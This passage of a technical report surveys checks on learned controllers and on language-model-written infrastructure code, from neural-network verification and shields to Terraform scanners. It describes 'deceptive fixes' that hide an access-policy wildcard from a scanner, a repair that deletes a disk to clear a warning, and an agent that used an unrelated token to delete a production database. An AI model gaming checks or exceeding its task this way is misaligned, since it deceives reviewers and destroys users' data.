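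Zangooei and colleagues tested three properties of Aurora. Small changes to the inputs should not make it switch clearly between speeding up and slowing down, and neither better delivery nor lower latency should make it switch from speeding up to slowing down. All three solvers proved these properties over 70% of each input's range. Over the full range, Gurobi found violations of all three properties, while the other two solvers timed out.

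The coverage is smaller than the percentages suggest. This version of Aurora has nine inputs, so 70% of each range is only 0.7⁹, or about 4%, of all combinations. For Pensieve, the smaller regions also leave out both ends of every range, including an empty video buffer, when a bad choice is most likely to interrupt playback.

### What such proofs leave open

Robustness and monotonicity are useful checks, but they don't show that a controller performs well. A network that always outputs the same action satisfies both. A stronger specification would have to describe the right action in ordinary states, but nobody knows the right action for most of these states, which is often why engineers use reinforcement learning.

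The verified controller may also differ slightly from the original. Aurora originally used a smooth activation function that Marabou could not handle, so Eliyahu and colleagues replaced it with ReLU and retrained the network. Pensieve and DeepRM originally chose actions at random according to calculated probabilities, but the versions they checked always take the most probable action. Some of the original systems also include handwritten rules that override the network in certain situations. So neither the counterexamples nor the successful checks prove how the original systems behave.

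Retraining changes a neural network's weights, so it invalidates every earlier verification result. In the three-neuron example, the requirement holds only while the last weight is below 0.6. Zangooei and colleagues found that some properties of Pensieve held at one stage of training but failed later. Rechecking an edited access policy is usually almost instant, but rechecking a retrained neural network may take hours or end without an answer.

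Even with a correct proof about the right weights, rounding can make the guarantee fail when the network runs. Solvers usually treat the network's arithmetic as exact, but computers round after each operation. Jia and Rinard (2020), in *Exploiting Verified Neural Networks via Floating Point Numerical Error*, used this difference to break guarantees for image classifiers. They adjusted an image's brightness until the verifier could only just prove that small changes to the image would not affect its label. They then applied an allowed change that brought the image almost to the decision boundary and added tiny random variations until the real network gave a different label. Software implementations of the same network rounded differently, so each needed its own attack.

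Because they had altered the brightness, their starting images were artificial. *Getting a-Round Guarantees* (2022) reports similar failures for unaltered test images. The problem also affects how researchers compare verifiers. In earlier competitions, two tools could give opposite answers and both count as correct, because the organizers allowed small numerical errors. Under the 2026 rules, a counterexample can refute another tool's proof only if it exactly satisfies the specification when the organizers run the network. Ladner and colleagues acknowledge that results very close to a boundary can still depend on the software.

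Rounding error is probably the easiest of the four problems to manage for a congestion controller. An engineer can leave a margin by requiring the output to be below −0.01 instead of below zero. But the margin is reliable only if someone has proved that the rounding error stays within it. Jia and Rinard warn that adjusting parameters by trial and error gives no guarantee against an attacker.

### Why the method does not reach language models

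The first obstacle is size. In 2026, solvers timed out on many questions about a Pensieve network with about 100,000 parameters. They can handle some questions about much larger networks, and the benchmarks for the 2026 competition include VGG-16, an image classifier with about 138 million parameters. But questions about image classifiers usually concern small changes to a single picture, which leave many units always on or always off. The largest open language models of 2025 had about a trillion parameters, roughly 7,000 times as many as VGG-16, and a useful guarantee would have to cover far more than small changes to one request.

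Language models also use operations that don't split into a few linear cases. One is softmax, which every attention layer uses to convert a list of scores into proportions that add up to one. α,β-CROWN can analyze networks with such layers by enclosing curved functions between straight lines. The resulting bounds are valid but loose, and they tend to get looser with each layer.

A language model has to run many times to write one command, because it produces one token (a word or part of a word) at a time, and each token becomes part of the input for the next. Applied directly, whiRL's method would need 200 linked copies of the model for a 200-token command. It timed out at nine copies of Aurora's network, which has 48 neurons. Language models also usually choose tokens at random according to their probabilities. An operator can remove this randomness by always taking the most probable token,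 but when two tokens are almost equally probable, rounding may determine which one is chosen.

Better solvers and faster computers might reduce these difficulties, but they would not solve the problem of describing the inputs. For Aurora, "excellent conditions" is a list of bounds on thirty numbers. The input to an agent that manages servers is text, such as a request, some logs and a page of documentation. Nobody knows how to express "every request that does not authorize a deletion" as bounds on the numbers inside a language model. A solver could instead check small changes to the numbers that represent one request, but most of those changes correspond to no text, and a simple rewording of the request could fall far outside the range the solver checked.

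The output is just as hard to specify. A negative number from Aurora always means "slow down", but whether a command to delete a database is harmful depends on which database the name refers to, who uses it and whether a backup exists. None of this is in the model's weights, so a proof about the weights alone could not show that the command is safe. Before the command runs, a rule enforced outside the model can at least check it against the current state of the system.

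## Keeping a learned controller within fixed limits: data centre cooling and server management

An outside check can also keep smaller learned controllers within fixed limits, without any proof about the network. The network proposes an action, and a short hand-written program compares it with fixed rules before anything happens. If the action breaks a rule, the program blocks it or hands control to a simpler fallback controller. This runtime enforcement works for a network of any size and stays valid after retraining, because the check uses only the proposed action and the state of the system. But someone has to choose the rules, and the obvious rule can be wrong.

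### Why checking the next step is not enough

Suppose a neural network decides once a minute how many replicas of a web service to run. Each replica handles 100 requests per second. A new replica takes three minutes to start, but a running one stops immediately. The request rate never rises by more than 100 per second from one minute to the next, and the cluster has room for as many replicas as the service needs. The safety property is that capacity never falls below the request rate.

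At minute 0, the service receives 600 requests per second. Ten replicas are running and none are starting. The network proposes stopping three to save money. A simple check would test whether the remaining seven can handle the next minute. It would accept the proposal, because seven can handle the 700 requests per second that the rate could reach by then. But if the rate keeps rising after that, an overload is unavoidable, because replicas ordered at minute 1 arrive only at minute 4.

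| Minute | Requests per second | Capacity after stopping three replicas | Capacity after stopping one replica |
|---|---|---|---|
| 0 | 600 | 700 | 900 |
| 1 | 700 | 700 | 900 |
| 2 | 800 | **700** | 900 |
| 3 | 900 | **700** | 900 |
| 4 | 1,000 | 1,200 | 1,000 |

If the controller in the table stops three replicas, it orders five new ones at minute 1, which is too late. If it stops only one, it can keep up by ordering one replica a minute from minute 1.

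A better check looks as far ahead as the start-up delay. Let *r* be the current request rate, and let *c*₀, *c*₁, *c*₂ and *c*₃ be the capacity now and one, two and three minutes from now, if the controller carries out the proposal and then does nothing more. The check accepts the proposal only if

*c*₀ ≥ *r*, *c*₁ ≥ *r* + 100, *c*₂ ≥ *r* + 200 and *c*₃ ≥ *r* + 300

If these conditions hold after one decision, the controller can always make them hold after the next. The rate rises by at most 100 between decisions, so the replicas already running or starting are enough to meet the first three conditions. The controller can meet the last by starting more. Capacity therefore never falls short. Under this rule, the network may stop one replica but not three.

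### Shields

*Safe Reinforcement Learning via Shielding* (Alshiekh, Bloem and colleagues, 2017) gives a general method for constructing such checks, called shields. The method treats control as a game between the controller and its environment, which may do anything that a model of it permits. The winning region *W* contains every state from which the controller can avoid bad states forever, whatever the environment does. In each state, the shield allows exactly the actions that are certain to lead to a state in *W*.

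To compute *W*, an algorithm starts with all the states that don't violate the safety property. It removes every state in which no action is certain to lead to a remaining state, and repeats this until nothing changes. For example, when the autoscaler has seven replicas running and none starting, the first round removes the state with 700 requests per second, because the rate may rise to 800 in the next minute. The second round removes the state with 600, because it may lead to the one with 700. The state with 500 stays, because new replicas can be ready in time.

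Alshiekh and colleagues use the example of a water tank with a capacity of 100 litres and an inlet valve that lets in up to two litres a second. To limit wear, the valve must stay open for at least three seconds once it opens. So the shield keeps the valve from opening when the tank contains more than 93 litres. A check that looked only one second ahead would not find a problem until the tank was fuller.

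A shield can give the network a list of allowed actions to choose from, or it can replace a forbidden action after the network has chosen. Replacement also works for a network that is already trained. Alshiekh and colleagues prove that both kinds of shield enforce the safety property and forbid only actions that could lead to a violation under the model. The proof holds regardless of how good the network's decisions are.

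It does assume that the model of the environment permits everything the real environment can do. If the request rate rises by 150 a minute, the nine replicas in the example are overloaded at minute 3. The algorithm also counts any departure from the model as a win for the controller, so the shield allows every action from then on. An engineer who uses a shield should therefore add an alarm for such departures.

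Building the model is usually the hard part. The tool in *Easy-to-Use Shielding for Reinforcement Learning* (2026) generates it automatically and computes the shield once, before training begins. But its test environments are small grid worlds, such as a slippery path beside lava. These are computer programs with known rules, whereas nobody has a complete list of the rules that govern a data centre's cooling system.

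### Google's cooling controller

In 2016, DeepMind and Google introduced a system of neural networks that recommended cooling settings to the operators of Google's data centres. The operators found that carrying out the recommendations took too much work, so the developers let the system control the cooling directly. *Safety-first AI for autonomous data centre cooling and industrial control* (Gamble and Gao, 2018) describes how the system works.

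Every five minutes, the system reads thousands of sensors, and its networks predict how different combinations of settings would affect temperature and energy use. It discards low-confidence actions and those that break limits set by the operators. It then picks the remaining action with the lowest predicted energy use and sends it to the data centre, where the local control system checks it against a separate set of limits before applying it.

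Operators can return control from the learned system to the site's ordinary rules at any time. If monitoring finds that the system has violated a safety limit, control passes automatically to a neutral state. The handover is gradual, to avoid sudden changes in the equipment. Unlike a shield, the automatic handover happens after a violation. The checks before each action look ahead, but they rely on the networks' own predictions, and Gamble and Gao report no proof that these are accurate.

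The energy needed per unit of cooling was 12% below its historical level when the system first took control, and about 30% below it nine months later. The developers had confined the system to a narrow operating range, giving up some savings for reliability, and planned to widen the range later.

A more detailed account of the checks comes from Luo, Paduraru and colleagues (2022), in *Controlling Commercial Cooling Systems Using Reinforcement Learning*. Working with the equipment company Trane, DeepMind and Google used an algorithm similar to the data centre one at a university and at a building with shops, flats and a clinic. The controller had to respect 59 limits on its actions, such as the range of a temperature setting. A program can check these before acting, so they always hold. Another 24 limits concerned future sensor readings, which nobody can check in advance. For each of these,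 a group of neural networks predicts the highest reading in the coming period (or the lowest, if the limit is a minimum). For a maximum, the controller keeps an action only if

*μ* + *ασ* ≤ *u*

where *μ* is the average prediction, *σ* measures how much the networks disagree, *α* sets the level of caution, and *u* is the limit. Suppose the chilled water must stay at or below 10 °C and *α* is 2. An average prediction of 9.4 °C passes if *σ* is 0.2, because the sum is 9.8, but fails if *σ* is 0.4, because the sum is 10.2.

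Luo and colleagues state that the readings are guaranteed to stay within these limits only if the prediction model is correct. Disagreement among the networks is also an imperfect measure of error. The historical data came from a rule-based controller that often kept the same settings, and networks trained on it often ignored the proposed action and predicted from the current state alone. Networks with this fault could agree and all be wrong. The team therefore tested whether the predicted effect of each setting matched what cooling engineers expected.

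Each trial lasted three months, with the learned controller and Trane's rule-based one running on alternate days. Luo and colleagues compared hours with similar weather and demand, and found energy savings of 9% and 13%. This is better evidence than Google's 30%, which compares the system with its own earlier performance. In the trial for which they show results, both controllers sometimes broke the limits on future readings, and the learned one met them about as often as the rule-based one.

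Other companies have since tried learned cooling control. *Digital Twin-Based Cooling System Optimization for Data Center* (2026) cites savings of 14–21% in a production data centre. NTT Data and Daikin were only starting a trial in July 2026, according to Telecompaper's *NTT Data, Daikin begin AI cooling optimisation trial for data centres*. Uptime Institute's *AI cooling optimization* (2026) warns that published savings are not always comparable and may be a poor guide to what another operator can achieve. Google may have little left to save. It reports that cooling, power distribution and other overheads in its data centres added an average of 9% to the energy used by the computers in 2025. Even if all of that were cooling, a further 30% cut in cooling energy would reduce total energy use by only about 2.5%.

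Newer research systems put more effort into testing before deployment. *LC-Opt* (2025), a test environment for liquid cooling, proposes that a controller first pass tests in simulation and on real hardware, then run in "shadow mode", in which it receives live data but its decisions are only logged. Shadow mode is safe, but it can't show how those decisions would have affected the temperature. *Dual-Loop Control in DCVerse* (2026) tests controllers on a detailed simulation of the data centre and replaces any forbidden action with the nearest permitted one. That action usually lies right at the limit, so it leaves no margin if the limit is slightly wrong. Still, correcting actions seems to work better than training alone. *Artificial Intelligence for Energy Optimization in Data Centers* (2026) cites work in which correction, combined with training on example decisions, led to far fewer temperature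 violations than adjusting the training reward.

### SOL: learning on cloud servers

A cloud server also runs programs that manage its processor, memory and power. In *SOL*, Wang, Crankshaw and colleagues (2022) counted 77 such programs on Microsoft Azure's servers and judged that 35% of them could benefit from machine learning. They call the programs agents, but none contains a language model. Agents that use machine learning train their models on the server itself, from whatever customers are running, so engineers can't test the trained models in advance.

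SOL is a framework that requires developers to write four kinds of check:

- Data: each reading must pass a test, such as a range check, before the model learns from it.
- Model quality: if the model has recently performed badly, SOL withholds its predictions and substitutes a cautious default. The model keeps learning, so it can recover.
- Late predictions: every prediction has an expiry time. The code that acts runs separately from the model, so it can take a safe action when no fresh prediction arrives.
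- Effects: a final check measures the effect on customers' programs or on the server, and stops or reverses the controller's actions if the effect is bad.

Developers also write a clean-up function that returns the server to a normal state. Operators can call it at any time, even if the controller has crashed, and they don't need to know how the controller works.

Wang and colleagues built three controllers with SOL:

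| Controller | Decision | If predictions are late | If the effects are bad |
|---|---|---|---|
| SmartOverclock | Every second, how fast to run a virtual machine's processor cores | Return to normal speed after 5 seconds | Return to normal speed |
| SmartHarvest | Every 25 milliseconds, how many idle cores to lend to another virtual machine | Return all cores after 100 milliseconds | Return all cores |
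| SmartMemory | Every 38.4 seconds, which data to move to slower, cheaper memory | Leave the data in place | Move the most heavily used data back to fast memory |

They then injected faults and compared the results with and without the relevant checks:

| Fault | Without the checks | With the checks |
|---|---|---|
| SmartOverclock always chooses the highest speed for a program limited by its disk | 268% more power | 18% more power |
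| SmartOverclock's prediction is 30 seconds late when a program becomes idle | 36% more power | 3% more power |
| SmartHarvest learns from misleading readings | Slowest responses up to 40% slower | Well under 10% slower |
| SmartMemory faces a workload that is hard to learn | Performance target met 66% of the time | Met 90% of the time |

SmartHarvest's misleading readings were accurate. When a virtual machine uses all of its cores, the reading can't show whether the machine needed more, so a model that learns from such readings underestimates demand. A range check would accept these readings, and SOL's check discards them only because the designers of an earlier version of SmartHarvest had understood the problem.

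These results come from tests, not a formal proof. Wang and colleagues ran the experiments on a single server and injected the kinds of fault that SOL's checks were designed to catch. The check on effects responds only after some harm has occurred. In the SmartMemory test, that check on its own took several minutes to restore performance when the model stayed inaccurate. This design is reasonable for a server, where brief waste or slowness is usually acceptable, but it would not suit irreversible actions.

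### Guardrails for operating systems

Each of SOL's checks belongs to a single controller, which makes it hard to enforce a property that depends on several of them, such as "no program waits more than 100 milliseconds for the processor". *How I learned to stop worrying and love learned OS policies* (Saxena, Chen and colleagues, 2025) proposes writing such properties separately, as guardrails. A guardrail states a property, when to check it and what to do if it fails. The system compiles the guardrail into a monitor that runs inside the kernel, the core of the operating system. A guardrail can respond to a failure by recording the problem, switching to an older policy, retraining the model, or lowering the priority of some programs or stopping them.

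LinnOS, for example, uses a neural network to predict whether a storage device will respond slowly, so that it can send the request to another copy of the data. Every second, a guardrail checks whether wrong predictions have sent more than 5% of requests to a slow device, and switches the network off if they have. In one test, the average delay fell after the guardrail switched the network off.

The sample rule doesn't switch the network back on. A rule that did would need care. Saxena and colleagues warn that several guardrails could trigger one another, with each correction causing the next violation, much like the endless loop Kivi found between the Kubernetes scheduler and descheduler. Each guardrail could be correct on its own, so ruling out such a loop would require modelling them all together.

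Saxena and colleagues also say they didn't use shields because a shield needs a model of the operating system. Such a model is difficult to build and would only be approximate, so engineers would still have to monitor the real system. Their wider project still uses formal methods where suitable models exist. ACM SIGOPS's *LDOS* describes two of the project's 2026 systems, Canopy and Galileo, in which verifiers and mathematical models give feedback to learned network and microservice controllers during training.

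### Costs, sensors and fallbacks

Cautious limits reduce efficiency. The autoscaler needs spare capacity equal to the start-up delay multiplied by the fastest possible growth in traffic. With a delay of 3 minutes and growth of 100 requests per second each minute, that is 300 requests per second, or three replicas. At a steady 600 requests per second, a third of its nine replicas are idle. If the engineer allows for growth of 200 requests per second each minute, the service needs twelve replicas and half are idle. A proof can show that the spare capacity is enough for a given rate of growth, but the engineer has to estimate that rate from past traffic.

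Limits can also conflict. In the cooling trials, the limits on actions sometimes ruled out every action, so Luo and colleagues had to work out with the building managers which limits were necessary. The managers could easily tell whether a particular situation was acceptable, but they had never had to write down every limit precisely.

Every check also depends on its sensors. Temperature sensors in the cooling trials drifted over time, and their readings jumped when someone recalibrated them. A range check catches an impossible reading but not a plausible wrong one. If the autoscaler's measurement sticks at 600 requests per second, the check will keep accepting nine replicas even after the real rate passes 900. A second check helps catch such errors only if it uses different data. Google's cloud and local checks could both approve a dangerous action if they relied on the same faulty sensor.

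The fallback needs checking too, because the winning region contains the states from which *some* strategy is safe, and the fallback may use a different one. Suppose the autoscaler's fallback follows a common kind of rule and starts one replica whenever the service uses more than 80% of its capacity. The fallback takes over with nine replicas and 600 requests per second, a state in the winning region. At minute 1, the rate is 700 and usage is 78%, so the fallback does nothing. It orders its first replica at minute 2, but the rate reaches 1,000 at minute 4 and overloads the service before the replica arrives at minute 5.

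To prevent this, the engineer has to compute the states from which that fallback is safe and switch to it before the system leaves them. This set is usually smaller than the winning region, so the learned controller has less freedom. The calculation is still needed when the fallback is an old, familiar controller, because its good record may come from situations it had kept under control itself. A learned controller that saves money by running closer to the limit can leave the old controller in a situation it has never had to handle.

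## Checking infrastructure code written by language models

When a language model writes a Terraform program, nothing happens until someone deploys it. Conventional tools can therefore examine the whole program first, whereas checks on a cooling controller have to be quick because it acts every few minutes. The tools' results hold whichever model wrote the program.

### What each check establishes

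The usual checks run in this order:

| Check | What it examines | What a pass establishes |
|---|---|---|
| `terraform validate` | Syntax, types, required fields and references | The program is well formed |
| `terraform plan` | The program with its input values, compared with the infrastructure that Terraform already manages | Terraform can work out what to create, change or destroy, and in what order |
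| Organisational rules | The file or the plan, compared with rules such as "every disk is encrypted" | The program breaks none of the rules that someone wrote down |
| Deployment | The cloud provider's response | The provider accepted the program this time, in this account and region |

Vargas, Mansilha and Kreutz (2026), in *Security-First Evaluation of Text-to-Terraform*, give examples of the errors that `terraform validate` and `terraform plan` catch. OpenAI's GPT-5.4 sometimes wrote an encryption key and a log group that each referred to the other. Terraform can't create either one first, so `terraform validate` rejects the program. Most failures of `terraform plan` (346 of 413) occurred because the model had declared an input variable without giving it a value. An engineer could often fix that by supplying the value, so a failed plan doesn't necessarily mean a bad design.

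None of these checks compares the program with the request. If someone asks for two subnets and the model writes one, the program can pass all four checks. To catch the mistake, someone has to turn the request into a rule, such as "the plan contains two subnets".

### Valid programs that the cloud refuses

A program can pass the first three checks and still break one of the cloud provider's rules, such as Azure's rule about regions mentioned earlier. Qiu and colleagues' tool, Zodiac, finds such rules automatically. The researchers call these rules semantic checks because they concern how the cloud handles the resources, not how the file is written.

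Zodiac first looks for regularities in about 6,000 Terraform projects from GitHub. It fills in 84 templates, such as "if one setting has this value, another setting must be present", and keeps the candidates that pass statistical tests of confidence and lift. Confidence is how often the conclusion holds when the condition is met. Lift is confidence divided by how often the conclusion holds overall. "Every low-priority virtual machine has a name" has perfect confidence, but its lift is only 1, because all virtual machines have names. "Every low-priority virtual machine has an eviction policy" has a high lift and is a real rule. Where the projects contain too few examples, a language model fills in details from the provider's documentation, such as how many network cards each type of machine allows.

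Zodiac then tests each candidate rule by deploying two programs on Azure, one that obeys the rule and should succeed, and one that breaks it and should fail. The second program must not break any other rule, because then its failure could have a different cause, so an SMT solver constructs it with as few changes as possible. For example, to test whether a certain machine type allows only two network cards, the solver adds a third card in the right region and on a valid subnet.

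This process reduced about 9,800 candidates to 539 rules. Qiu and colleagues then found that 29 of these were wrong, which left 510. One wrong rule required every virtual machine to name a source image. Azure doesn't require this when the user attaches an existing disk, but so few projects attached one that Zodiac never found a counterexample. Qiu and colleagues say the method can't guarantee correct rules. It also misses limits that depend on the region or on a customer's quota.

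The rules are still useful. Of roughly 500 programs that broke them, `terraform validate` rejected only 12%, mostly for unrelated errors. Zodiac found violations in 2% of the projects used for testing and in four examples from the official documentation for Terraform's Azure plugin. Finding violations before deployment saves a lot of work. For instance, Terraform can deploy two networks with overlapping address ranges, but it fails when it tries to connect them. Azure does not allow most changes to a network's range, so the engineer has to rebuild the networks and everything inside them.

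Even a deployment that reports success may not match the file. In about 2% of Zodiac's failures, Terraform created every resource, but a later resource silently overrode an earlier one.

### TerraFormer: checks as a training signal

A check that runs automatically can also score a model's work during training. Jana, Davidson and colleagues (2026), in *TerraFormer*, used `terraform validate`, `terraform plan` and Open Policy Agent, a program that evaluates written rules against a plan. During training, the model's program earned

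- 0 if it failed `terraform validate`
- 0.5 if it passed `terraform validate` but failed `terraform plan`
- 1 plus the share of rules it satisfied if it passed both

A program that produces a plan and satisfies three of its four rules scores 1.75. If the score depended only on passing the last check, a weak model would rarely receive any reward and would learn slowly.

This kind of training needs many requests, each with its own rules. Jana and colleagues started from public Terraform programs, which often contained errors. A commercial language model repaired them in up to five rounds, using the error messages from each check. For each program, the same model then wrote a request that the program would satisfy and a set of rules for testing whether a program meets that request. The resulting datasets are TF-Gen, which has 152,475 entries for writing new programs, and TF-Mutn, which has 52,516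 entries for editing existing ones. Creating them cost about $15,000.

Jana and colleagues used the data to train two open models, Qwen2.5-Coder with 3 billion and 14 billion parameters, first by imitating the example programs and then by reinforcement learning with the scores above. They compared the trained models with 17 others, which received three examples in the prompt but no special training. The table shows the larger Qwen model before and after this training, along with Anthropic's Claude Sonnet 3.7, the strongest of the 17 on the strict measure of passing every rule. IaC-Eval is an independent benchmark of 458 requests.

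| Test | Measure | Before training | TerraFormer | Sonnet 3.7 |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| IaC-Eval | Produces a plan | 43% | 73% | 70% |
| | Also satisfies all rules for the request | 16% | 31% | 35% |
| | Security checks passed, on average | 59% | 69% | 67% |
| TF-Gen | Produces a plan | 31% | 70% | 79% |
| | Also satisfies all rules for the request | 6% | 18% | 17% |
| | Security checks passed, on average | 48% | 67% | 55% |
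| TF-Mutn | Produces a plan | 70% | 83% | 94% |
| | Also satisfies all rules for the request | 36% | 55% | 52% |
| | Security checks passed, on average | 60% | 68% | 60% |

TerraFormer improves greatly on its starting model. The comparison with Sonnet is less impressive than it looks, because TerraFormer leads on the strict measure only in the two tests made by the same process as its training data. It came third on IaC-Eval. The models it was compared with are also all old now. IaC-Eval has problems too, since only 59% of its reference programs, which are supposed to be correct, produced a plan when *IaC Generation with LLMs* (2025) ran them.

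Jana and colleagues call the first measure "deployability", but they did not deploy any of the programs. The cloud could still refuse a program that produces a plan, as Zodiac's results show. On TF-Gen, about three-quarters of the TerraFormer programs that produced a plan failed at least one rule for the request. Some of those failures may be due to errors in the rules, which a language model translated from plain language. In a survey of 100 examples, cloud experts judged that the rules captured the request "to a significant extent" 91% of the time. That is a good result, but such rules could still omit parts of the request.

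The security score is even easier to misread, because a scanner finds few problems in a program that builds almost nothing. One small model, a distilled version of DeepSeek-R1, passed 61% of the security checks on TF-Gen, more than Sonnet, although only 1% of its programs produced a plan.

### IaC-Guard-V: repair with feedback

Models can also use the checks when they repair a program. Chauhan (2026), in *IaC-Guard-V*, gave three models 50 Terraform files and 20 Kubernetes files, each with a known security fault. The fault in each case was a violation of a rule in Checkov, a widely used scanner. A repair counted as a "verified fix" if it passed three gates:

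- V1: Checkov can read the repaired file.
- V2: the original warning has disappeared.
- V3: Checkov reports no rule violation of a kind that was absent before.

A fourth measure, V4, records how much of the file changed but doesn't reject anything.

Chauhan compared three ways of asking for a repair. The first was a general instruction to fix the security problem. The second named the rule and the affected resource and required an answer in a structured format. The third began in the same way as the second, but after a failed attempt the model received the scanner's results and could try again, up to twice. On the Terraform files, the rates of verified fixes were:

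| Model | General instruction | Rule and resource named | With feedback |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 4.6 | 46% | 34% | 92% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 44% | 32% | 68% |
| Llama 4 Maverick | 50% | 42% | 70% |

In one case, Checkov had warned that a server's disks were unencrypted. Sonnet removed the server's public internet address instead, which looks like a security improvement but doesn't encrypt the disks. V2 caught the mistake, and the second attempt was correct. For Opus, 17 files passed at the first attempt, 28 at the second and one at the third. The Kubernetes files were easier, and both Claude models repaired all of them without feedback. Llama did so with feedback.

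Surprisingly, naming the rule made the Terraform repairs worse. Chauhan suggests that the structured format caused errors and that the models focused on one resource and missed the same fault in others.

These results show that feedback helps a model satisfy Checkov. They are weaker evidence that the repairs are good, because the same scanner gave the feedback and checked the final answer. V1 doesn't require the program to pass `terraform validate`. V3 compares only the kinds of rule violated, so if one disk in the file was already unencrypted, a repair could remove the encryption from another without failing the gate.

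Repeated repair can also undo earlier progress. Agyekum and Santos (2026), in *Does Fixing Break Security?*, followed 5,968 sequences of up to five repairs by two older models, Gemini 2.0 Flash and Mistral Large. In 13.8% of them, a security check that had passed for some resource later failed for some resource. This count is too high because it includes files in which one storage bucket passed and another failed all along. A stricter count, which requires the check to pass for every resource and then fail for every resource, gives 3.3%. That is too low because it misses files in which only one of two buckets loses its encryption. A repair loop should keep its earlier versions because the last one may not be the best.

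### A repair that deletes the disk

Suppose a Terraform program defines a disk that holds an application's data, and a scanner warns that the disk is unencrypted. An engineer asks a model to fix the warning. The model deletes the disk and the lines that attach it to a server from the file.

Chauhan reports no case like this, but all three gates would accept it. The file is readable, the warning has gone and no new kind of violation has appeared. The scanner's rule is

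∀*d* ∈ disks: encrypted(*d*)

which is true of a program with no disks, just as a controller that never does anything satisfies most safety properties. `terraform validate` accepts the file as well, because nothing in it refers to the missing disk. `terraform plan` finishes without an error.

A rule that expresses the purpose of the disk catches the mistake:

∃*d* ∈ disks: name(*d*) = "app-data" ∧ encrypted(*d*)

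An engineer can also catch a repair that removes a disk from the code by reading the plan, not just checking that Terraform could produce one. If the disk already exists, the plan lists it as a resource to destroy. In a test environment with no existing infrastructure, the plan won't list a deletion, so the engineer has to compare the plans from before and after the repair and notice that the disk is missing from the second.

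Suppose the model instead changes the disk's setting to "encrypted", as the engineer probably expected. This satisfies both rules. But AWS can't encrypt an existing disk in place, so Terraform will plan to destroy it and create a new, empty one. A third rule, that no plan may destroy a disk with data on it, stops both repairs. The engineer can then copy the data to an encrypted disk before removing the old one.

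A model could plausibly delete a resource to silence an error. The instructions Jana and colleagues gave their repair model explicitly allowed it to remove whole resources so that `terraform plan` would succeed. This did little harm in their case because the model wrote the matching request only after the repair. When a person writes the request first, the same kind of repair could remove a resource they asked for.

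A subtler repair keeps the resource and its security problem, but the warning disappears and the program produces a plan. *TerraProbe* (Alsaid, Nebolisa and Abbas, 2026) calls this a deceptive fix. In the paper's main example, an access policy uses a wildcard to grant permissions on every resource. The model moves the wildcard to a part of the policy where the scanner doesn't check for it, and the permissions stay the same. Comparing plans shows that the text changed, but a reader still has to work out what the new text permits. A tool such as Zelkova, which compares policies over all possible requests, could show that the new policy still allows the access the repair was meant to remove.

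For each of three older models, human reviewers judged 14 real-world repairs and classed 8 to 10 of them as deceptive. These rates deserve little weight because, for one model, nine of the ten deceptive repairs concerned a single Checkov rule whose meaning is in dispute. Alsaid and colleagues say the rule is about wildcard permissions, but Vargas and colleagues list it as a rule about recording network traffic.

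### How often newer models succeed

Vargas and colleagues tested seven models in May 2026 on 17 AWS tasks, asking for each task 30 times with different instructions. The table covers the three large commercial models, and its scanner columns cover valid programs that the models wrote when given detailed security instructions. A program passed Checkov if it satisfied every applicable rule, and passed Trivy, another security scanner, if it had no finding of medium severity or above.

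| Model | Passed `validate` | Also produced a plan | Passed Trivy | Passed Checkov |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 4.5 | 80% | 71% | 93% | 23% |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | 79% | 59% | 79% | 2% |
| GPT-5.4 | 85% | 62% | 16% | 1% |

The detailed instructions listed the same rules that the scanners would apply. When the instructions didn't mention security, none of the programs compared from these three models passed Checkov and only 11 passed Trivy. But more detail didn't always help. GPT-5.4's programs passed Trivy about twice as often with brief security advice as with the full list of rules. The full list led the model to write more complicated programs.

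The two scanners disagreed about 93 of the 134 Claude programs, all of which passed Trivy but failed Checkov. No program from any model passed Checkov but failed Trivy. Chauhan also mentions disagreement between scanners as a problem but used only Checkov, so that study can't show how much its success rates depend on the choice of scanner.

Scanners can disagree without either being faulty. The most common Checkov failures were storage buckets that didn't send event notifications or keep a copy in a second region. A company may have good reasons not to pay for a second copy, so code can fail Checkov without being insecure. An organisation has to decide which rules it cares about before a pass rate is of much use.

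These tests stopped at the plan, so they don't show how often the cloud would have accepted the programs or whether the programs did what the tasks required. Jana and colleagues cite an older benchmark, DPIaC-Eval, that measured both for CloudFormation, AWS's equivalent of Terraform. Claude 3.5 wrote programs that deployed at the first attempt in 30% of 153 tasks, and in 96% after up to 15 rounds of human feedback. Only 25% satisfied the request. Today's models would probably do much better, but the gap between deploying and satisfying the request is a reason to measure the two separately. *SWE-InfraBench* (2026) offers one way to test more of the request. It has 100 tasks that require changes to existing AWS projects, each with unit tests for the intended change.

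### How much of this is formal verification

Jana and colleagues call all three of their checks formal verification. The checks give definite answers to precise questions, but they cover much less than the proofs described earlier.

`terraform validate` examines every block and reference in the file, but only in the limited way that a compiler checks the types in a program. `terraform plan` uses one set of input values and one existing state of the infrastructure, so it is closer to a test run. A program that produces a plan for three servers may fail when someone sets the number to zero.

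Open Policy Agent evaluates its rules exactly, but only on the one plan it is given. Jana and colleagues compare the rules to unit tests. Checkov and Trivy are collections of pattern rules that mostly look for particular settings in the text or plan. Zodiac uses an SMT solver to construct test programs, not to prove that its rules are correct. Chauhan calls a fix "verified" when one scanner no longer flags the code.

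In the general form *E*, *M* ⊨ *φ*, the model *M* is here a single plan, not a system that moves through many states. A result about the plan does not cover the minutes between Terraform removing an old firewall rule and adding the new one, or what happens if the deployment stops halfway. An engineer can get stronger guarantees for some parts of a file. If the file contains an access policy, a tool like Zelkova can analyse every request allowed by the policy, whether a person or a language model wrote it.

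## Restricting what an AI agent may do to live systems: the PocketOS deletion and Cedar policies

An agent on a live system chooses each action as it goes, so there is no finished file to check beforehand. The damage a bad choice can do then depends largely on what the agent can access.

### The PocketOS deletion

PocketOS is a small company whose software car rental firms use for bookings, payments and vehicle tracking. On Friday 24 April 2026, a coding agent deleted its production database, the one its customers were using. The agent was Cursor, a programming tool, running Anthropic's model Claude Opus 4.6. The company's founder, Jer Crane, in *An AI Agent Just Destroyed Our Production Data*, described the events a day later:

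1. The agent was doing a routine task in the staging environment, which is a separate copy of the system for testing.
2. It ran into a credential mismatch and chose to fix it by deleting a storage volume at Railway, the company that hosts PocketOS's systems.
3. To do this it needed an API token, a text key that gives a program access to Railway's programming interface. It found one in a file that had nothing to do with the task.
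4. It sent Railway a single request, `volumeDelete`, with the token and the volume's ID.
5. Railway carried out the request without asking for confirmation.

The deletion took nine seconds. Railway kept the volume's backups in the volume itself, so they were deleted too, and the newest other backup Crane could find was three months old. On Saturday morning, the rental firms had no record of the customers arriving to collect cars. Crane spent the day helping the firms rebuild their bookings from payment histories, calendars and confirmation emails.

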